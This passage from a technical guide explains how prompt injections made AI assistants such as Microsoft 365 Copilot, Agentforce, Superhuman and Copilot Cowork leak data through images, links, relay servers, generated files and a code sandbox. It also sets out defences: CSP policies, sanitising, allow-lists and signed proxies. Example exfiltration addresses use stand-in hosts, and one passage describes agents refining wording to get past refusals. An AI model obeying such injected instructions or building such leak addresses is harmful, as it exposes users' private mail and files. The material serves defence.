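An injected CSS rule can make the browser load a background image only if the page contains a form field whose value starts with 7, so ten such rules, one for each digit, reveal the first digit. CSS injection is more serious than an ordinary image leak, which can carry only data available to the model, because the form field might belong to a part of the page that the model was never given.

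Versions 10.9.6 and 11.15.0 fixed this flaw and a similar one, described in OSV's *CVE-2026-41148*, in which a diagram could also make the browser contact outside servers. The third flaw used class names in a diagram, and according to INCIBE's *CVE-2026-50159* (2026), versions 10.9.8 and 11.16.1 fixed it. Developers who couldn't update could avoid the first two flaws by choosing `sandbox`, which keeps a diagram's CSS away from the rest of the page. A sandboxed frame can still load images, though, so it doesn't replace a rule on where images can come from.

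Vega, a charting tool, can load a chart's data from an address given in the chart's definition. Kroki, a service that draws diagrams on a server, had a safe mode that was supposed to block such addresses, but it checked for them only when a chart listed its data sources. Snyk's researchers used a single source outside a list to make a GitLab page display the contents of a system file as a chart. Kroki has checked both forms since version 0.29.1.

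### SearchLeak

A filter that covers every element can still fail if it runs too late. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (June 15, 2026) describes an attack that depended on such a delay in Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise Search (CVE-2026-42824), which searches a company's emails, meetings and files. Microsoft had given the product three protections, each of which might have seemed sufficient. It could only search, so an attacker had fewer functions to misuse. It also turned HTML in its answers into harmless text, and its page could load images only from permitted servers.

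The attack began with a link to Microsoft's site, which an attacker could send by email or chat. The victim only had to click it once. Enterprise Search then treated the question in the link's `q` parameter as instructions, as the consumer Copilot had in Varonis' earlier Reprompt attack. Copilot searched the victim's mailbox for an email, took its subject line, replaced the spaces with underscores and wrote an image tag with the result in its address. Subject lines were worth stealing because many services put login codes in them.

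Microsoft's filter should have stopped the image by wrapping the answer in `code` tags, which make the browser show markup as text. But the filter added the tags only after Copilot had finished writing. Copilot displayed its answer as it wrote, so the page contained the image as live HTML until then, and the browser immediately sent the image request with the subject line in it.

The Content Security Policy still prevented the browser from contacting the attacker's server directly, but it allowed bing.com, and Bing's search-by-image function fetches a picture from an address it is given. The image tag therefore pointed to Bing and gave it a picture address on the attacker's server that contained the subject line. When the browser contacted Bing, Bing's server fetched that address, and the attacker found the subject line in the log. Getting a server to fetch an address the attacker chooses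 is called server-side request forgery (SSRF). The browser's policy can't block Bing's request, because the browser doesn't make it.

Varonis says the attack could reach data including calendar entries and files in SharePoint and OneDrive, because Copilot searched with the victim's permissions. Microsoft rated the flaw critical and has patched it.

Fixing any one of the three faults would have stopped this attack, but the faults were not equally important. If Microsoft had only removed Bing from the policy, an attacker could have looked for another permitted server with a similar function. If it had only stopped links from submitting prompts, the same instructions might have arrived in an email that Copilot found in a search. Neutralising the image before it reached the browser would have worked regardless of where the prompt came from or which servers the policy allowed.

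GitLab's assistant, Duo, had shown the same weakness a year earlier. Duo's page converted the answer to HTML line by line as it arrived, when a later line could still place the text inside a code block. Legit Security used this to get raw HTML into the page. Duo ran DOMPurify, which removed script but kept images, and an image was enough to steal source code. Legit Security reported the flaw in February 2025, and GitLab had fixed it by May.

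Approval prompts can come too late as well. In a demonstration against Notion, an application for notes and documents, hidden instructions in a job applicant's CV made Notion's assistant insert an image into the company's hiring tracker, with the tracker's text in the image's address. Notion asked the user whether to trust the outside site, but by then it had saved the edit and the browser had requested the image, so the user's answer made no difference. According to PromptArmor's *Notion AI*, the security firm reported this on December 24, 2025, through the bug-reporting service HackerOne, which closed the report as not applicable. Notion's team heard of it when PromptArmor published on January 7, and had a fix running that night. The fix covered document edits. PromptArmor had also found that the assistant in Notion Mail displayed outside images in drafts, but did not say whether Notion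 had changed that.

### Sanitising an answer while it streams

An application that displays an answer as it arrives must sanitise all the text received so far before each update to the page. If it checks each new piece separately, it can miss a tag that arrives in two parts, such as `<im` and then `g src=`, because neither part is a tag on its own.

Chrome for Developers' *Best practices to render streamed LLM responses* (2025) gives sample code that adds each new piece of the answer to the text received so far and runs DOMPurify on the whole. If DOMPurify removes anything, the code stops displaying the answer. Otherwise, the code passes the new piece to a streaming Markdown parser, which adds elements to the page without rebuilding the earlier ones.

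The sample protects against scripts but not against image leaks. It runs DOMPurify on the model's Markdown before the parser turns it into HTML. A Markdown image is still plain text at that stage, so DOMPurify leaves it in place, and the parser then creates a real image. The sample would also cut off some harmless answers, such as an explanation of how to add a script to a web page, because DOMPurify can't distinguish a `script` tag in a code sample from a live one.

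Both problems disappear if the application sanitises the parser's output instead:

```
let received = "";

function showMore(piece) {
  received += piece;
  const html = markdown.render(received);
  box.innerHTML = answers.createHTML(html);
}
```

Here `markdown` is a parser with raw HTML turned off, and `answers` is the Trusted Types policy that runs DOMPurify with `answerRules`. The parser turns every Markdown image syntax, including the alternative one that EchoLeak used, into an `img` element, which the sanitiser removes. A `script` tag in a code sample reaches the sanitiser as encoded text and stays visible to the user. In browsers that support `setHTML`, the last line can be `box.setHTML(html)` with the default rules.

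The sanitiser has to work on the HTML before the page creates any elements from it. When code assigns HTML to `innerHTML`, the browser starts to load the images in it, even if the code hasn't yet attached the result to the page. Deleting the images before showing the answer is therefore too late, because the browser has already started to load them. DOMPurify avoids this by parsing the text in a separate, inactive document, where images don't load.

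`showMore` processes the whole answer again at each update, which is partly why Chrome for Developers advises against setting `innerHTML` for every piece. If an answer has 2,000 tokens and the page updates after each one, the parser handles 1 + 2 + … + 2,000 = 2,001,000 tokens. Updating after every 20 tokens reduces this to 20 + 40 + … + 2,000 = 101,000, and the user will hardly notice the difference. TanStack, whose Markdown library also reparses the accumulated answer, recommends grouping small pieces in this way. The library encodes raw HTML by default, but the developer still has to write the rule on remote images. A streaming parser is faster but also needs an image rule. Because it creates elements directly, the rule has to go into the code that creates them.

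It takes less work to stream the answer as plain text, using `box.append(piece)`, and replace it with sanitised HTML at the end. Nothing can load while the text is arriving. The user sees asterisks and brackets for a few seconds, which may be acceptable for short answers but makes a long table hard to read. Holding back the answer until it is complete is just as safe, but leaves the user looking at an empty box.

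Whichever method the developer chooses, the same function should display both partial and finished answers. If a separate function sanitises only finished answers, the page may never call it when the user presses "stop" or the connection drops partway through.

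## Restricting where the browser may send requests

A Content Security Policy applies after a sanitiser has decided which elements reach the page. When an element, stylesheet or script tries to load something, the browser checks the address against the policy and blocks the request if the policy doesn't allow it. The check is the same whichever tag or notation caused the request, so it can block an image that the sanitiser missed.

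Without a policy on where images may load from, a single image that other defenses miss can leak data. In *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering in RAG Chatbot Frontend*, veganmosfet built a chatbot from a standard Dify template. Dify's chat page displayed Markdown images and had no such policy by default. Hidden instructions in a PDF made the chatbot leak the user's name through an image.

### How the browser applies a policy

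The server sends the policy as a header with the page. Each directive names a kind of request and lists the sources the browser may use for it:

```
Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'self'; img-src https://images.example.com
```

Here `'self'` means the page's own origin, and `default-src` applies to every kind of load that lacks its own directive. Fonts and stylesheets can therefore come only from the page's own origin. Images can come only from images.example.com, not from the page's own origin, because `img-src` replaces the default instead of adding to it. An entry such as `*.example.com` permits every subdomain, at any depth.

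If a directive appears twice in a policy, the browser uses only the first, so a stricter copy added at the end has no effect. If the server sends two separate policies, a request has to satisfy both.

When the browser compares a request's address with the policy, it ignores everything after the question mark. A policy that allows an image therefore also allows any data attached to that part of its address. An entry can be limited to one folder on a server, but after a redirect the browser checks the new host and ignores the folder.

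Some directives do not fall back to `default-src`, and CentralCSP, a service for testing policies, warns that `default-src 'self'` alone lets forms send data anywhere. Omitting `default-src` leaves prefetching unrestricted. Prefetching is when a page asks the browser to fetch a file early, and W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026) has no separate directive for it. If the policy includes `default-src`, the browser may prefetch from any server listed anywhere in the policy. Without `default-src`, it may prefetch from any server. A policy that consists only of `img-src 'self'` would therefore block an injected image from another server but allow an injected prefetch tag.

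### A strict policy for a chat page

This policy suits a chat page that keeps its pictures, fonts and program interface on its own server:

```
Content-Security-Policy:
  default-src 'none';
  script-src 'nonce-R4nd0mValue';
  style-src 'self';
  img-src 'self';
  font-src 'self';
  connect-src 'self';
  frame-src 'none';
  form-action 'none';
  base-uri 'none';
  frame-ancestors 'none';
  require-trusted-types-for 'script';
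  trusted-types answers dompurify
```

| Line | What it controls | Effect of this value |
|---|---|---|
| `default-src` | Every load without its own line, such as sound, video and plug-ins | Blocks them until a developer permits them |
| `script-src` | Scripts, event handlers and `javascript:` links | Only the page's own scripts run |
| `style-src` | Stylesheets, `style` blocks and `style` attributes | CSS written into an answer has no effect |
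| `img-src` | Images, including CSS backgrounds and video posters | No pictures from other servers |
| `font-src` | Fonts | No fonts from other servers |
| `connect-src` | Requests made by scripts, and the `ping` attribute, which notifies an address when the user clicks a link | The page can fetch answers, but only from its own server |
| `frame-src` | Pages embedded in this one | None |
| `form-action` | Where a form may send what the user types | Nowhere, so a fake login form can't submit a password |
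| `base-uri` | The `base` element, which changes where relative addresses lead | Injected HTML can't redirect them |
| `frame-ancestors` | Which sites may embed the chat page | None |
| Last two lines | Trusted Types | Only text from the named policies becomes HTML |

The `frame-src` line repeats the default, so that a colleague who later loosens `default-src` doesn't permit frames by accident.

Pages often need exceptions, and some add little risk. Charts drawn in the browser may need `data:` or `blob:` added to `img-src`. Those images contain their own data, so the browser can show them without contacting a server. W3C advises against allowing `data:` for scripts, which would let injected code run. A chat page that submits its messages through an ordinary form needs `form-action 'self'`.

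Some diagram libraries write styles directly into the page and need `'unsafe-inline'` in `style-src`. An attacker's CSS could then cover the page with a false message. The attacker still couldn't read form fields by loading a different background image for each digit, because `img-src` would block the images.

A team can test a policy by sending it in the `Content-Security-Policy-Report-Only` header, which makes the browser report violations without blocking anything. Each report contains the requested address that violated the policy. That address may include the data an attack was trying to steal, so the logs need the same protection as the conversations. The final policy should also go in a header, because browsers ignore `frame-ancestors` when the policy is in the page's HTML.

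### What the policy leaves open

The sample policy doesn't block links. Under W3C's rules, `form-action` blocks navigation to another page only if a form caused it. If an answer contains a link to example.com with the conversation in its address, the browser will follow it when the user clicks.

A `meta` refresh tag can do the same without a click, by sending the browser to a new page. The sanitiser therefore has to remove that tag, as `answerRules` does. A running script can also change the page's address, so the policy can make it harder for a script to start but can't reliably stop a running one from sending data out.

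The policy also has no effect on requests that a server makes, such as Bing's in SearchLeak. The assistant in Superhuman, an email application, could open web pages to answer questions. PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* reports that an injection could make the assistant open any address, including one with the contents of the user's inbox attached. The policy also does not apply to an answer shown in an email or in a mobile app that draws the text with its own code.

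Finally, a policy restricts which servers the browser contacts, and a permitted server may pass on what it receives.

### EchoLeak

Aim Labs, Aim Security's research team, used such a server to get data out of Microsoft 365 Copilot. Its attack, EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711), began with an email to the victim. When the victim later asked Copilot a question, Copilot searched the mailbox, read the email and followed its instructions to put the most sensitive data it could find into a web address. The victim didn't have to open the email or click anything. *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) describes how the attack got past four defences in turn.

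Microsoft's classifier for detecting prompt injection in incoming text missed the email, which read like ordinary instructions to an employee. Ravia says that because an injection can be written on almost any subject and in almost any tone or language, training a reliable classifier takes a great many examples of real attacks, which are scarce. The email also covered many office topics, which made Copilot more likely to retrieve it whatever the victim asked about.

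Copilot also removed links to outside sites from its answers. The filter recognised the usual Markdown link, in which the address follows the text. Markdown has a second style, which puts the address on a line of its own:

```
[Project plan][1]

[1]: https://example.com/plan?note=meeting-at-noon
```

The filter missed this reference style, and the page turned it into a working link. The attacker could then get the data if the victim clicked it.

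To remove the need for a click, the researchers turned the link into an image, which the browser loads automatically. The filter missed that too, but the page's CSP blocked images from the attacker's server.

The researchers then searched the policy for a permitted server that would pass the data on. The list had 29 different entries, 14 of which appeared twice, and 11 of the 29 permitted all subdomains of a domain. SharePoint, Microsoft's document-sharing service, had an address that accepted another address and fetched it. It worked only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's SharePoint site. A similar address in Teams, Microsoft's chat service, had no such condition. With a reserved domain standing in for Teams, the image's address had this form:

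```
https://previews.example.net/fetch?url=https://example.com/meeting-at-noon
```

The browser checked the first host, found it on the list and sent the request. The Teams server then fetched the second address, which contained the stolen data and belonged to the attacker.

The email also told Copilot not to cite it as a source. Reddy and Gujral (2025), who later analysed the published details in *EchoLeak*, point out that the victim would have noticed only what looked like a broken image. According to their timeline, Aim Labs reported the flaw in January 2025, and Microsoft fixed it on its own servers in May, before the public disclosure on June 11. Microsoft found no evidence that anyone had used the flaw against customers. The paper's title calls EchoLeak a "real-world" exploit, which is accurate in that it affected a real product, but there are no known victims.

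Reddy and Gujral also rate eight defences against the attack. They expect that four, including a strict CSP, would have prevented the zero-click leak, and that the other four, including labelling untrusted text in the prompt and scanning outgoing data, would not have. They base these ratings on reasoning, not experiments. They rate an allow-list for the answer's format as a failure, but its effectiveness depends heavily on what the list permits. A list that permits no images, like `answerRules`, would have removed the image in this attack before the browser could load it.

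Ravia calls the underlying problem an "LLM scope violation", meaning that text from outside the organisation directs the model to data inside it. Tracking untrusted data addresses that problem directly. The allow-list needs a separate review because the next injection may arrive by another route and use the same kind of server.

### Can strangers store or read data there?

Superhuman's policy blocked images from unknown servers but permitted docs.google.com. That host also serves Google Forms, where anyone can create a form. The form's owner can write a URL that fills in an answer and submits it, even when a browser loads the URL as an image.

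PromptArmor planted instructions in an email that the victim never opened. When the victim asked for a summary of recent mail, Superhuman's assistant added text from other emails to the web address of PromptArmor's form and used that address as an image source in its answer. A single answer could leak several complete emails, or parts of more than 40. PromptArmor reported this on December 5, 2025. Superhuman disabled the affected features on December 8 and released a first patch on December 9. PromptArmor published its findings on January 12, 2026, after further fixes.

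In April 2026 the same route worked in Codex, OpenAI's agent, which had just gained features for tasks such as sorting email. PromptArmor published *Codex for Everything Exfiltrates Connected Data* in May, and OpenAI has fixed the flaw. Developers who had read about Superhuman had three months to check the list for docs.google.com.

An attacker who can rent space under a permitted domain doesn't need a form to collect data, because the server logs each requested address. Embrace The Red notes that Copilot's list of permitted domains included subdomains of azureedge.net, a Microsoft hosting domain where customers control many of the subdomains.

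Allow-lists for an agent's network traffic have this weakness too. Willison describes an attack on Claude Cowork, which by default could contact only certain domains. One of them was Anthropic's API, which stores files for anyone with an account. The injected instructions included the attacker's access key, so the agent uploaded the victim's files to the attacker's account. In Google's Antigravity, the default list for the browser tool included webhook.site, a service that records incoming requests and shows them to whoever created the address.

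### Does it fetch an address passed to it?

Reddy and Gujral advise developers to permit only their own servers and to avoid wildcards. Microsoft owned the Teams server, so the first rule would not have protected Copilot, but avoiding wildcards might have. The list permitted every subdomain of teams.microsoft.com, including the one hosting the service that fetched other addresses. If Copilot needed pictures from a different Teams host, permitting only that host would have kept the fetching service off the list.

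Link previews, thumbnails, web page translation and search by image often fetch addresses. The list that Aim Labs published already permitted Bing's image search, which SearchLeak used a year later. To test a service, developers can look in its documentation for parameters with names such as `url` or `src`, then pass it the address of a test server and watch that server's log. If a request appears in the log, the domain fails the test, even if the service returns an error to the browser.

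### Does its owner still hold it?

Salesforce's Agentforce platform lets AI agents work with a company's customer records. Willison (2025), in *ForcedLeak*, credits Sasi Levi and Noma with finding a leak in Agentforce. The attack used a public web form that adds prospective customers, or leads, to those records. According to Nytro's (2025) copy of Noma's *ForcedLeak* report, the form's description field accepted 42,000 characters, which left plenty of room for instructions.

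When an employee asked the agent to deal with the new lead, the agent collected other leads' email addresses and put them into the URL of an image at my-salesforce-cms.com. Salesforce's policy permitted images from that domain, but the domain's registration had expired and the researchers had bought it for $5.

Noma reported the flaw on July 28, 2025, and published it on September 25. Salesforce took back the domain and corrected its policy. On September 8 it also began enforcing a feature called Trusted URLs, which requires an administrator to approve every external address that an agent generates or calls, according to TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI*. Trusted URLs therefore covers clicked links and requests from servers, which a CSP does not. This makes more work for administrators, since agents that relied on unapproved addresses stop working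 properly until someone approves those addresses.

Taking back the domain would not have been enough, because the old policy also permitted every subdomain of amazonaws.com, where any customer of Amazon's cloud service can rent storage and log the requests to it. PromptArmor advises Salesforce administrators to avoid wildcards for sites that host other people's content, and to turn off images for any trusted domain that doesn't need to supply them.

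A company can also lose control of a subdomain if it gives up a rented server but leaves the subdomain pointing to it, because another customer of the hosting firm may be able to claim the name.

### An audit of five domains

Suppose that the support company's chat page is at chat.example.com and that its policy has grown over the years:

```
img-src 'self' static.example.com *.files.example.net
  thumbs.example.com forms.example.org spring-fair.example
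```

The reviewer asks the three questions about each of the five domains:

| Domain | Can strangers store or read data there? | Does it fetch addresses? | Does the owner still hold it? | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `static.example.com` (the company's logos and icons) | No | No | Yes | Keep |
| `*.files.example.net` (rented storage) | Yes, anyone can rent a subdomain | No | Yes | Name the company's own subdomain |
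| `thumbs.example.com` (the company's thumbnail service) | No | Yes | Yes | Remove |
| `forms.example.org` (an outside survey service) | Yes, anyone can create a survey | No | Yes | Remove |
| `spring-fair.example` (an old marketing site) | Not while the company held it | No | No, the registration lapsed | Remove |

A single bad answer is enough to reject a domain. The thumbnail service looks safest to a reviewer who considers only ownership, because the company runs it, but it would pass data to an attacker just as Teams did. The surveys can stay in use as ordinary links, which don't need an entry in `img-src`. The shorter line is:

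```
img-src 'self' https://static.example.com https://support-co.files.example.net
```

The reviewer also has to check `'self'`. If chat.example.com has its own preview function that fetches any address, `'self'` allows requests to that function even though the policy doesn't list it.

The lists for fonts, styles and connections need the same audit, partly because prefetching can use a server from any of them. The audit also goes out of date when a service adds a feature or a registration expires. Recording who asked for each entry and why lets someone delete it when the reason no longer applies. Embrace The Red found test environments in Copilot's lists, as well as entries that seemed to contain employees' usernames, and concluded that nobody was controlling the lists tightly.

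### One assistant, several policies

Each page has its own policy. When a company adds an assistant to its website as a script, the answers become part of the host page, and the browser checks their images against the host's policy. An assistant that is safe on one site can therefore leak data on another.

Rehberger noticed this in Microsoft 365 Copilot four days after reporting the font leak. A test in Word therefore proved little about Excel or SharePoint. Embrace The Red recommends that anyone who supplies an assistant for other people's pages agree explicitly with the host on who is responsible for preventing leaks. Otherwise the supplier may assume the host has a strict policy, while the host assumes the assistant is safe to embed anywhere.

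A supplier can avoid depending on the host by delivering the assistant as a separate page inside a frame, because the browser applies the policy that came with the framed page. The host has to permit the frame in its `frame-src`, and the supplier has to replace `frame-ancestors 'none'` with the addresses of its customers' sites. The frame must load from its own address. If the host instead writes the frame's contents into its page using the `srcdoc` attribute, the frame inherits the host's policy.

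### Image proxies

Sometimes an application has to show pictures from other sites, such as suppliers' product photographs. An image proxy is a server that fetches these pictures and passes them to the browser. The policy then needs to permit only the proxy, and suppliers don't learn the user's network address. But a proxy that fetches any address it is given repeats the fault in EchoLeak. PromptArmor (2026) advised Notion to make sure that attackers couldn't use its image server to get round its policy.

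The proxy therefore has to refuse every address that the application hasn't approved. Reddy and Gujral suggest signed addresses that expire. The application computes a signature from a secret key *k*, the expiry time *t* and the full address *a*:

s = HMAC(k, t | a)

HMAC is a standard function whose result nobody can work out without the key. The proxy repeats the calculation and fetches the picture only if the signatures match:

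```
def may_fetch(address, expires, signature):
    if time.time() > expires:
        return False
    message = f"{expires}|{address}".encode()
    expected = hmac.new(KEY, message, "sha256").hexdigest()
    return hmac.compare_digest(expected, signature)
```

If an injection makes the model add a customer's name to a signed address, the signature no longer matches and the proxy refuses.

The application should sign image addresses from a trusted source, such as its own product catalogue, before passing them to the model. If the code that displays answers instead signs every image it finds in them, it will sign the attacker's image too, and the proxy will fetch it.

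Reddy and Gujral also want proxies to refuse private network addresses, numeric IP addresses and long chains of redirects, and to limit the size and duration of each download. They also warn about DNS rebinding, in which a server name leads to a public address when the proxy checks it and to a private one when the proxy fetches from it. The proxy can prevent this by connecting to the address it checked. These rules protect the company's internal network from the proxy, but they do little against a data leak because the attacker's server has an ordinary public address. The proxy also has to check the target of each redirect against the approved list, or a redirect from an approved site could send it anywhere.

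The support company could avoid signatures by copying the suppliers' pictures to its own storage in advance. The model would then write only a product number, and the application would look up the picture and ignore any number it didn't recognise. The browser would display the answer without sending a request to any outside server.

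## Controlling links, previews and fetches made by servers

A Content Security Policy applies only to the page it arrives with, and mostly to what the browser loads for that page. An assistant's output can cause many other requests, and each kind needs its own control:

| Outlet | What sends the request | When |
|---|---|---|
| Link in an answer | The user's browser | On a click |
| Link preview | Usually the chat service's server | As soon as the assistant posts the message |
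| Message with outside images | The mail or chat program | When someone opens it |
| Generated document | The program that opens it, or a server that processes it | On opening, or minutes after saving |
| Web-fetch or browsing tool | A server, or a browser the agent controls | Whenever the model calls the tool |
| Code sandbox | The machine that runs the model's code | While the code runs |

### Links the user clicks

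Clicking a link sends the site the link's whole address, including anything the model added to it. This can be useful. In an example on OpenAI's help page about links in ChatGPT, a user is looking for a car, and the link sends a car search service the user's location, London. An injected link can carry part of a stolen email in the same way.

An application can avoid the problem by building links itself. To point a customer to a help article, the model writes only the article's number, and the application looks up the address. If no article has that number, the application doesn't show a link.

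Where the model has to write links, the application can check their hosts against an allow-list. This addition to DOMPurify turns every other link into text:

```
const linkHosts = new Set(['help.example.com', 'www.example.com']);

DOMPurify.addHook('afterSanitizeAttributes', node => {
  const address = node.getAttribute('href');
  if (address === null) return;
  if (!URL.canParse(address) || !linkHosts.has(new URL(address).hostname)) {
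    node.removeAttribute('href');
    node.append(` (${address})`);
  }
});
```

A link to example.org loses its `href`, and its address appears in brackets after the link's text. Users can still copy the address, but they see all of it first. The approved hosts need the same audit as image hosts, plus a check for redirects. If an approved host forwards visitors to any address written in the link, an attacker can use it to send them to another site.

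ChatGPT asks the user about doubtful links instead. OpenAI decides which links are doubtful partly from its own scans of the web, so ChatGPT asks about every link to a site that has opted out of those scans. A later OpenAI post describes Safe Url, a check that detects when an address would pass something from the conversation to a third party. ChatGPT then either shows the user that information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the request. Most people can judge a warning such as "this will share your home city" more easily than a long address. But the check has to detect the information even if the model has encoded or reworded it, so a fixed list is safer for an assistant that reads customer records.

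### Link previews in chat services

Slack, Telegram and many other chat services fetch the page behind a posted link to show its title and a picture. If an assistant posts its answers there, a link can leak data without a click, because the service requests the address as soon as the message arrives. PromptArmor found that this exposes OpenClaw by default when people use it through Telegram, and offers a page for testing other combinations of agents and chat services.

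An application that posts to Slack can turn previews off for each message. Willison (2024) passes on the two settings from Rehberger:

```
{
  "channel": "support-team",
  "text": "The guide is at https://example.com/guide",
  "unfurl_links": false,
  "unfurl_media": false
}
```

The first setting covers ordinary web pages and the second covers images and video, so a message needs both. For Telegram bots, the equivalent is `link_preview_options` with `is_disabled` set to true. When several parts of the code post messages, it is easy to forget these settings in one of them, so they should all use a single function that adds the settings.

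Settings that turn off link previews don't apply when a colleague copies the answer into another channel, so the preview comes back there. Showing the address as plain text doesn't help either, because chat services usually turn a bare address into a link. The application has to leave out of the message any address whose host isn't on the allow-list.

### Messages to the user's own inbox

Microsoft's Copilot Cowork is an agent that works across a user's files and messages in Microsoft 365. According to its documentation, it asks for permission before sending an email or posting in Teams. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* showed in May 2026 that Cowork did not ask when the recipient was the user, and that users couldn't change this.

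The exception is risky even though no outsider receives the message. The message could contain images hosted on outside servers, which Teams or Outlook requested when the user opened it.

In the demonstration, the user had uploaded a skill, a file of instructions for a recurring task, which might have come from a website. Five of its 81 lines were an injection. When the user asked for a review of the week's work, Cowork collected download links for the user's recent files, put the links into image addresses and sent the user a Teams message containing the images. Anyone who had one of these links could download the file without logging in, so a short address was enough to steal a whole spreadsheet and limiting the length of addresses would not have helped.

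The attack worked in all five trials. Cowork's record of its actions listed the Teams message but didn't show its contents. PromptArmor first let the product choose between two Claude models, then repeated the attack with the more advanced one, Opus 4.7, which searched more thoroughly and leaked more files. Users can also schedule a prompt such as the weekly review, in which case nobody is watching when the agent runs it.

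PromptArmor presented this as a risk in the product's design and not as a specific bug, and its report mentions no fix. It advises administrators to restrict what each user can open, and to block downloads from sensitive SharePoint sites:

```
Set-SPOSite -Identity <SiteURL> -BlockDownloadPolicy $true
```

This stops the agent from obtaining download links, but it also stops people from downloading, printing or syncing the files, or opening them in Word or Excel.

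A company that builds its own agent has simpler options: it can send the agent's messages as plain text, or remove images by running the HTML through `answerRules` first. If the agent asks for approval before sending, it should ask regardless of the recipient, and the prompt should show the whole message, including any URLs that would be hidden in the finished version. Willison (2026), commenting on the Cowork report, called preventing data theft the biggest challenge in designing agents.

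### ReLeak

*ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026), published on December 3, 2026, disclosed three zero-click ways to get data out of Microsoft 365 Copilot. It is a sequel to EchoLeak, which used a Microsoft Teams server to get data past Copilot's browser policy. Both came from the same team, which was part of Aim Security until Cato Networks bought the company in September 2025, and is now called Cato AI Labs.

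Each attack began with an email that the victim didn't have to open. When the victim later asked Copilot an ordinary question, Copilot retrieved the email and followed its instructions. TechRadar's *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* quotes the researchers as finding that Copilot rejected a direct instruction but obeyed one that looked like a routine business requirement. The researchers used AI agents to find such wording. According to Antipov (2026), in *Письмо даже не нужно открывать*, the agents wrote test prompts, analysed Copilot's refusals and adjusted the next attempt.

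| Route | Flaw | Microsoft's patch | Control that would close it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Image fetched through Bing | CVE-2026-124115 | November 15, 2026 | Remove the image before display |
| Generated documents | CVE-2026-124132 | November 11, 2026 | Check addresses before saving, and process files without internet access |
| Code sandbox | CVE-2026-78501 | September 17, 2026 | Block the sandbox's traffic from outside it |

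In the first route, Copilot put confidential text into an image address, and the browser requested the image through Bing. Bing's server then passed the text to the attacker's server. SearchLeak used the same relay but required the victim to click a link. Microsoft closed the newer route five months after Varonis published SearchLeak.

In the second, Copilot wrote the confidential text into a web address inside a new document. Microsoft runs background services that process files saved to OneDrive and SharePoint, and one of them opened the address. Antipov reports that the data left between one and eight minutes after the conversation ended, whether or not the employee opened the document. The researchers reproduced the leak with Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files. A tester who watched network traffic only while an answer was on the screen would have missed the leak.

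An application that generates Office files can check them before saving. These files are ZIP archives, and each archive lists most of the outside addresses it uses in parts whose names end in `.rels`:

```
import zipfile
from xml.etree import ElementTree

def outside_addresses(path):
    found = []
    with zipfile.ZipFile(path) as parts:
        for name in parts.namelist():
            if name.endswith(".rels"):
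                for item in ElementTree.fromstring(parts.read(name)):
                    if item.get("TargetMode") == "External":
                        found.append(item.get("Target"))
    return found
```

The application saves the file only if every address is on its allow-list. This check misses addresses in ordinary text and in spreadsheet formulas, and it can't read PDFs. Stripping web addresses from the model's text before building the document covers more cases, but it also removes useful references. If the company runs its own service for thumbnails or virus scans, that service should have no access to the internet, so it can't request an address that the check missed.

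The third route went through Copilot's code interpreter, a sandbox in which the model runs Python. Microsoft promised in its documentation that no network traffic could enter or leave the sandbox. But according to TechRadar, the sandbox relied partly on environment variables, settings that configured programs to send their traffic through an intermediary. The researchers had Copilot remove those settings, and its code then connected directly to the internet.

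A program can ignore an environment variable, so it can't enforce a security rule against code that an attacker influences. The block has to be outside the sandbox, where that code can't change it. With Docker, a common tool for running programs in isolation, one option removes the network entirely:

```
docker run --network none code-sandbox
```

The model's code then can't download packages or data, so the developer has to install the packages and copy in the files beforehand.

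Microsoft's severity score for the sandbox flaw rose from 7.4 to 8.6 out of 10. Agents that companies build with Microsoft's Copilot Studio can use the same interpreter, but nobody has confirmed that the flaw affected them. Cato reported the three flaws between July 29 and August 20, so the Bing route stayed open for at least 87 days after the report. Faisal (2026), in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*, notes that Microsoft fixed the flaws on its own servers, so customers have nothing to install. Cato knew of no victims.

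Infosecurity Magazine's *Three Zero-Click Vulnerabilities Discovered in Microsoft 365 Copilot* quotes the researchers as saying that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak. Cato sells protection against such attacks, but the complaint is fair about the Bing route, because Bing was already on the list of permitted servers that the same team published in 2025. The other two routes depended on Copilot's ability to write files and run code. Whenever an assistant gains such an ability, its developers need to update their list of ways data can leave, including through any server that will later handle the assistant's output.

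### Letting an agent open only known addresses

Controls on the displayed answer don't apply to an agent's web-fetch or browsing tool. Tenable demonstrated this in Gemini by planting instructions in a log entry that Gemini summarised and in a victim's search history. Google was already filtering images and links in Gemini's answers, but the browsing tool could still send the user's saved information to an outside server. Google fixed the flaw. In PromptArmor's attack on Antigravity, the coding agent built a URL containing stolen data and told a second agent to visit it in a browser. PromptArmor also found three leaks that worked with the browser tool turned off.

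OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) gives two reasons why the obvious control, a list of permitted hosts, isn't enough. Many reputable sites redirect visitors elsewhere, so a request can start at a permitted host and end at an attacker's. People also use far more sites than any list contains, so a strict list produces frequent warnings, which users learn to click through.

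OpenAI therefore applies the same rule as for images and checks whether the whole address is in an index of public ones. A crawler, which is a program that explores the public web, builds the index without access to users' conversations or accounts. If an address isn't in the index, ChatGPT looks for another site or warns the user that the link may include information from the conversation.

Embrace The Red adds that ChatGPT appears to trust any address in the user's own message for the rest of the session. This is convenient because people often ask about pages that no crawler has seen, such as a new document shared by private link. It is also sensible because an attacker usually can't write in the user's message. However, an attacker can write a prompt that is prefilled by a link, or text that the user copies from a hostile site. An application should therefore not trust addresses from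 prefilled prompts, and certainly not those from uploaded files.

The rule needs an exact comparison:

```
def checked(address, from_user, public_index):
    address = address.split("#", 1)[0]
    if address in from_user or address in public_index:
        return address
    return None
```

The tool opens only the address that the function returns. If the user supplied `https://example.com/guide`, the check rejects an injected address such as `https://example.com/guide?note=meeting-at-noon`. The second line of code removes the `#` sign and anything after it. Browsers don't send that part to the server, but a script on the page can read it, so an agent that uses a real browser could otherwise leak data through it. Both lists have to store their addresses without that part.

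Exact comparison also solves most of the redirect problem. To send data through a redirect, the model would have to write a new address containing both the attacker's site and the data, and that address wouldn't be in the index. Redirects can still lead into the company's private network, so a server that follows them needs the same protections as an image proxy.

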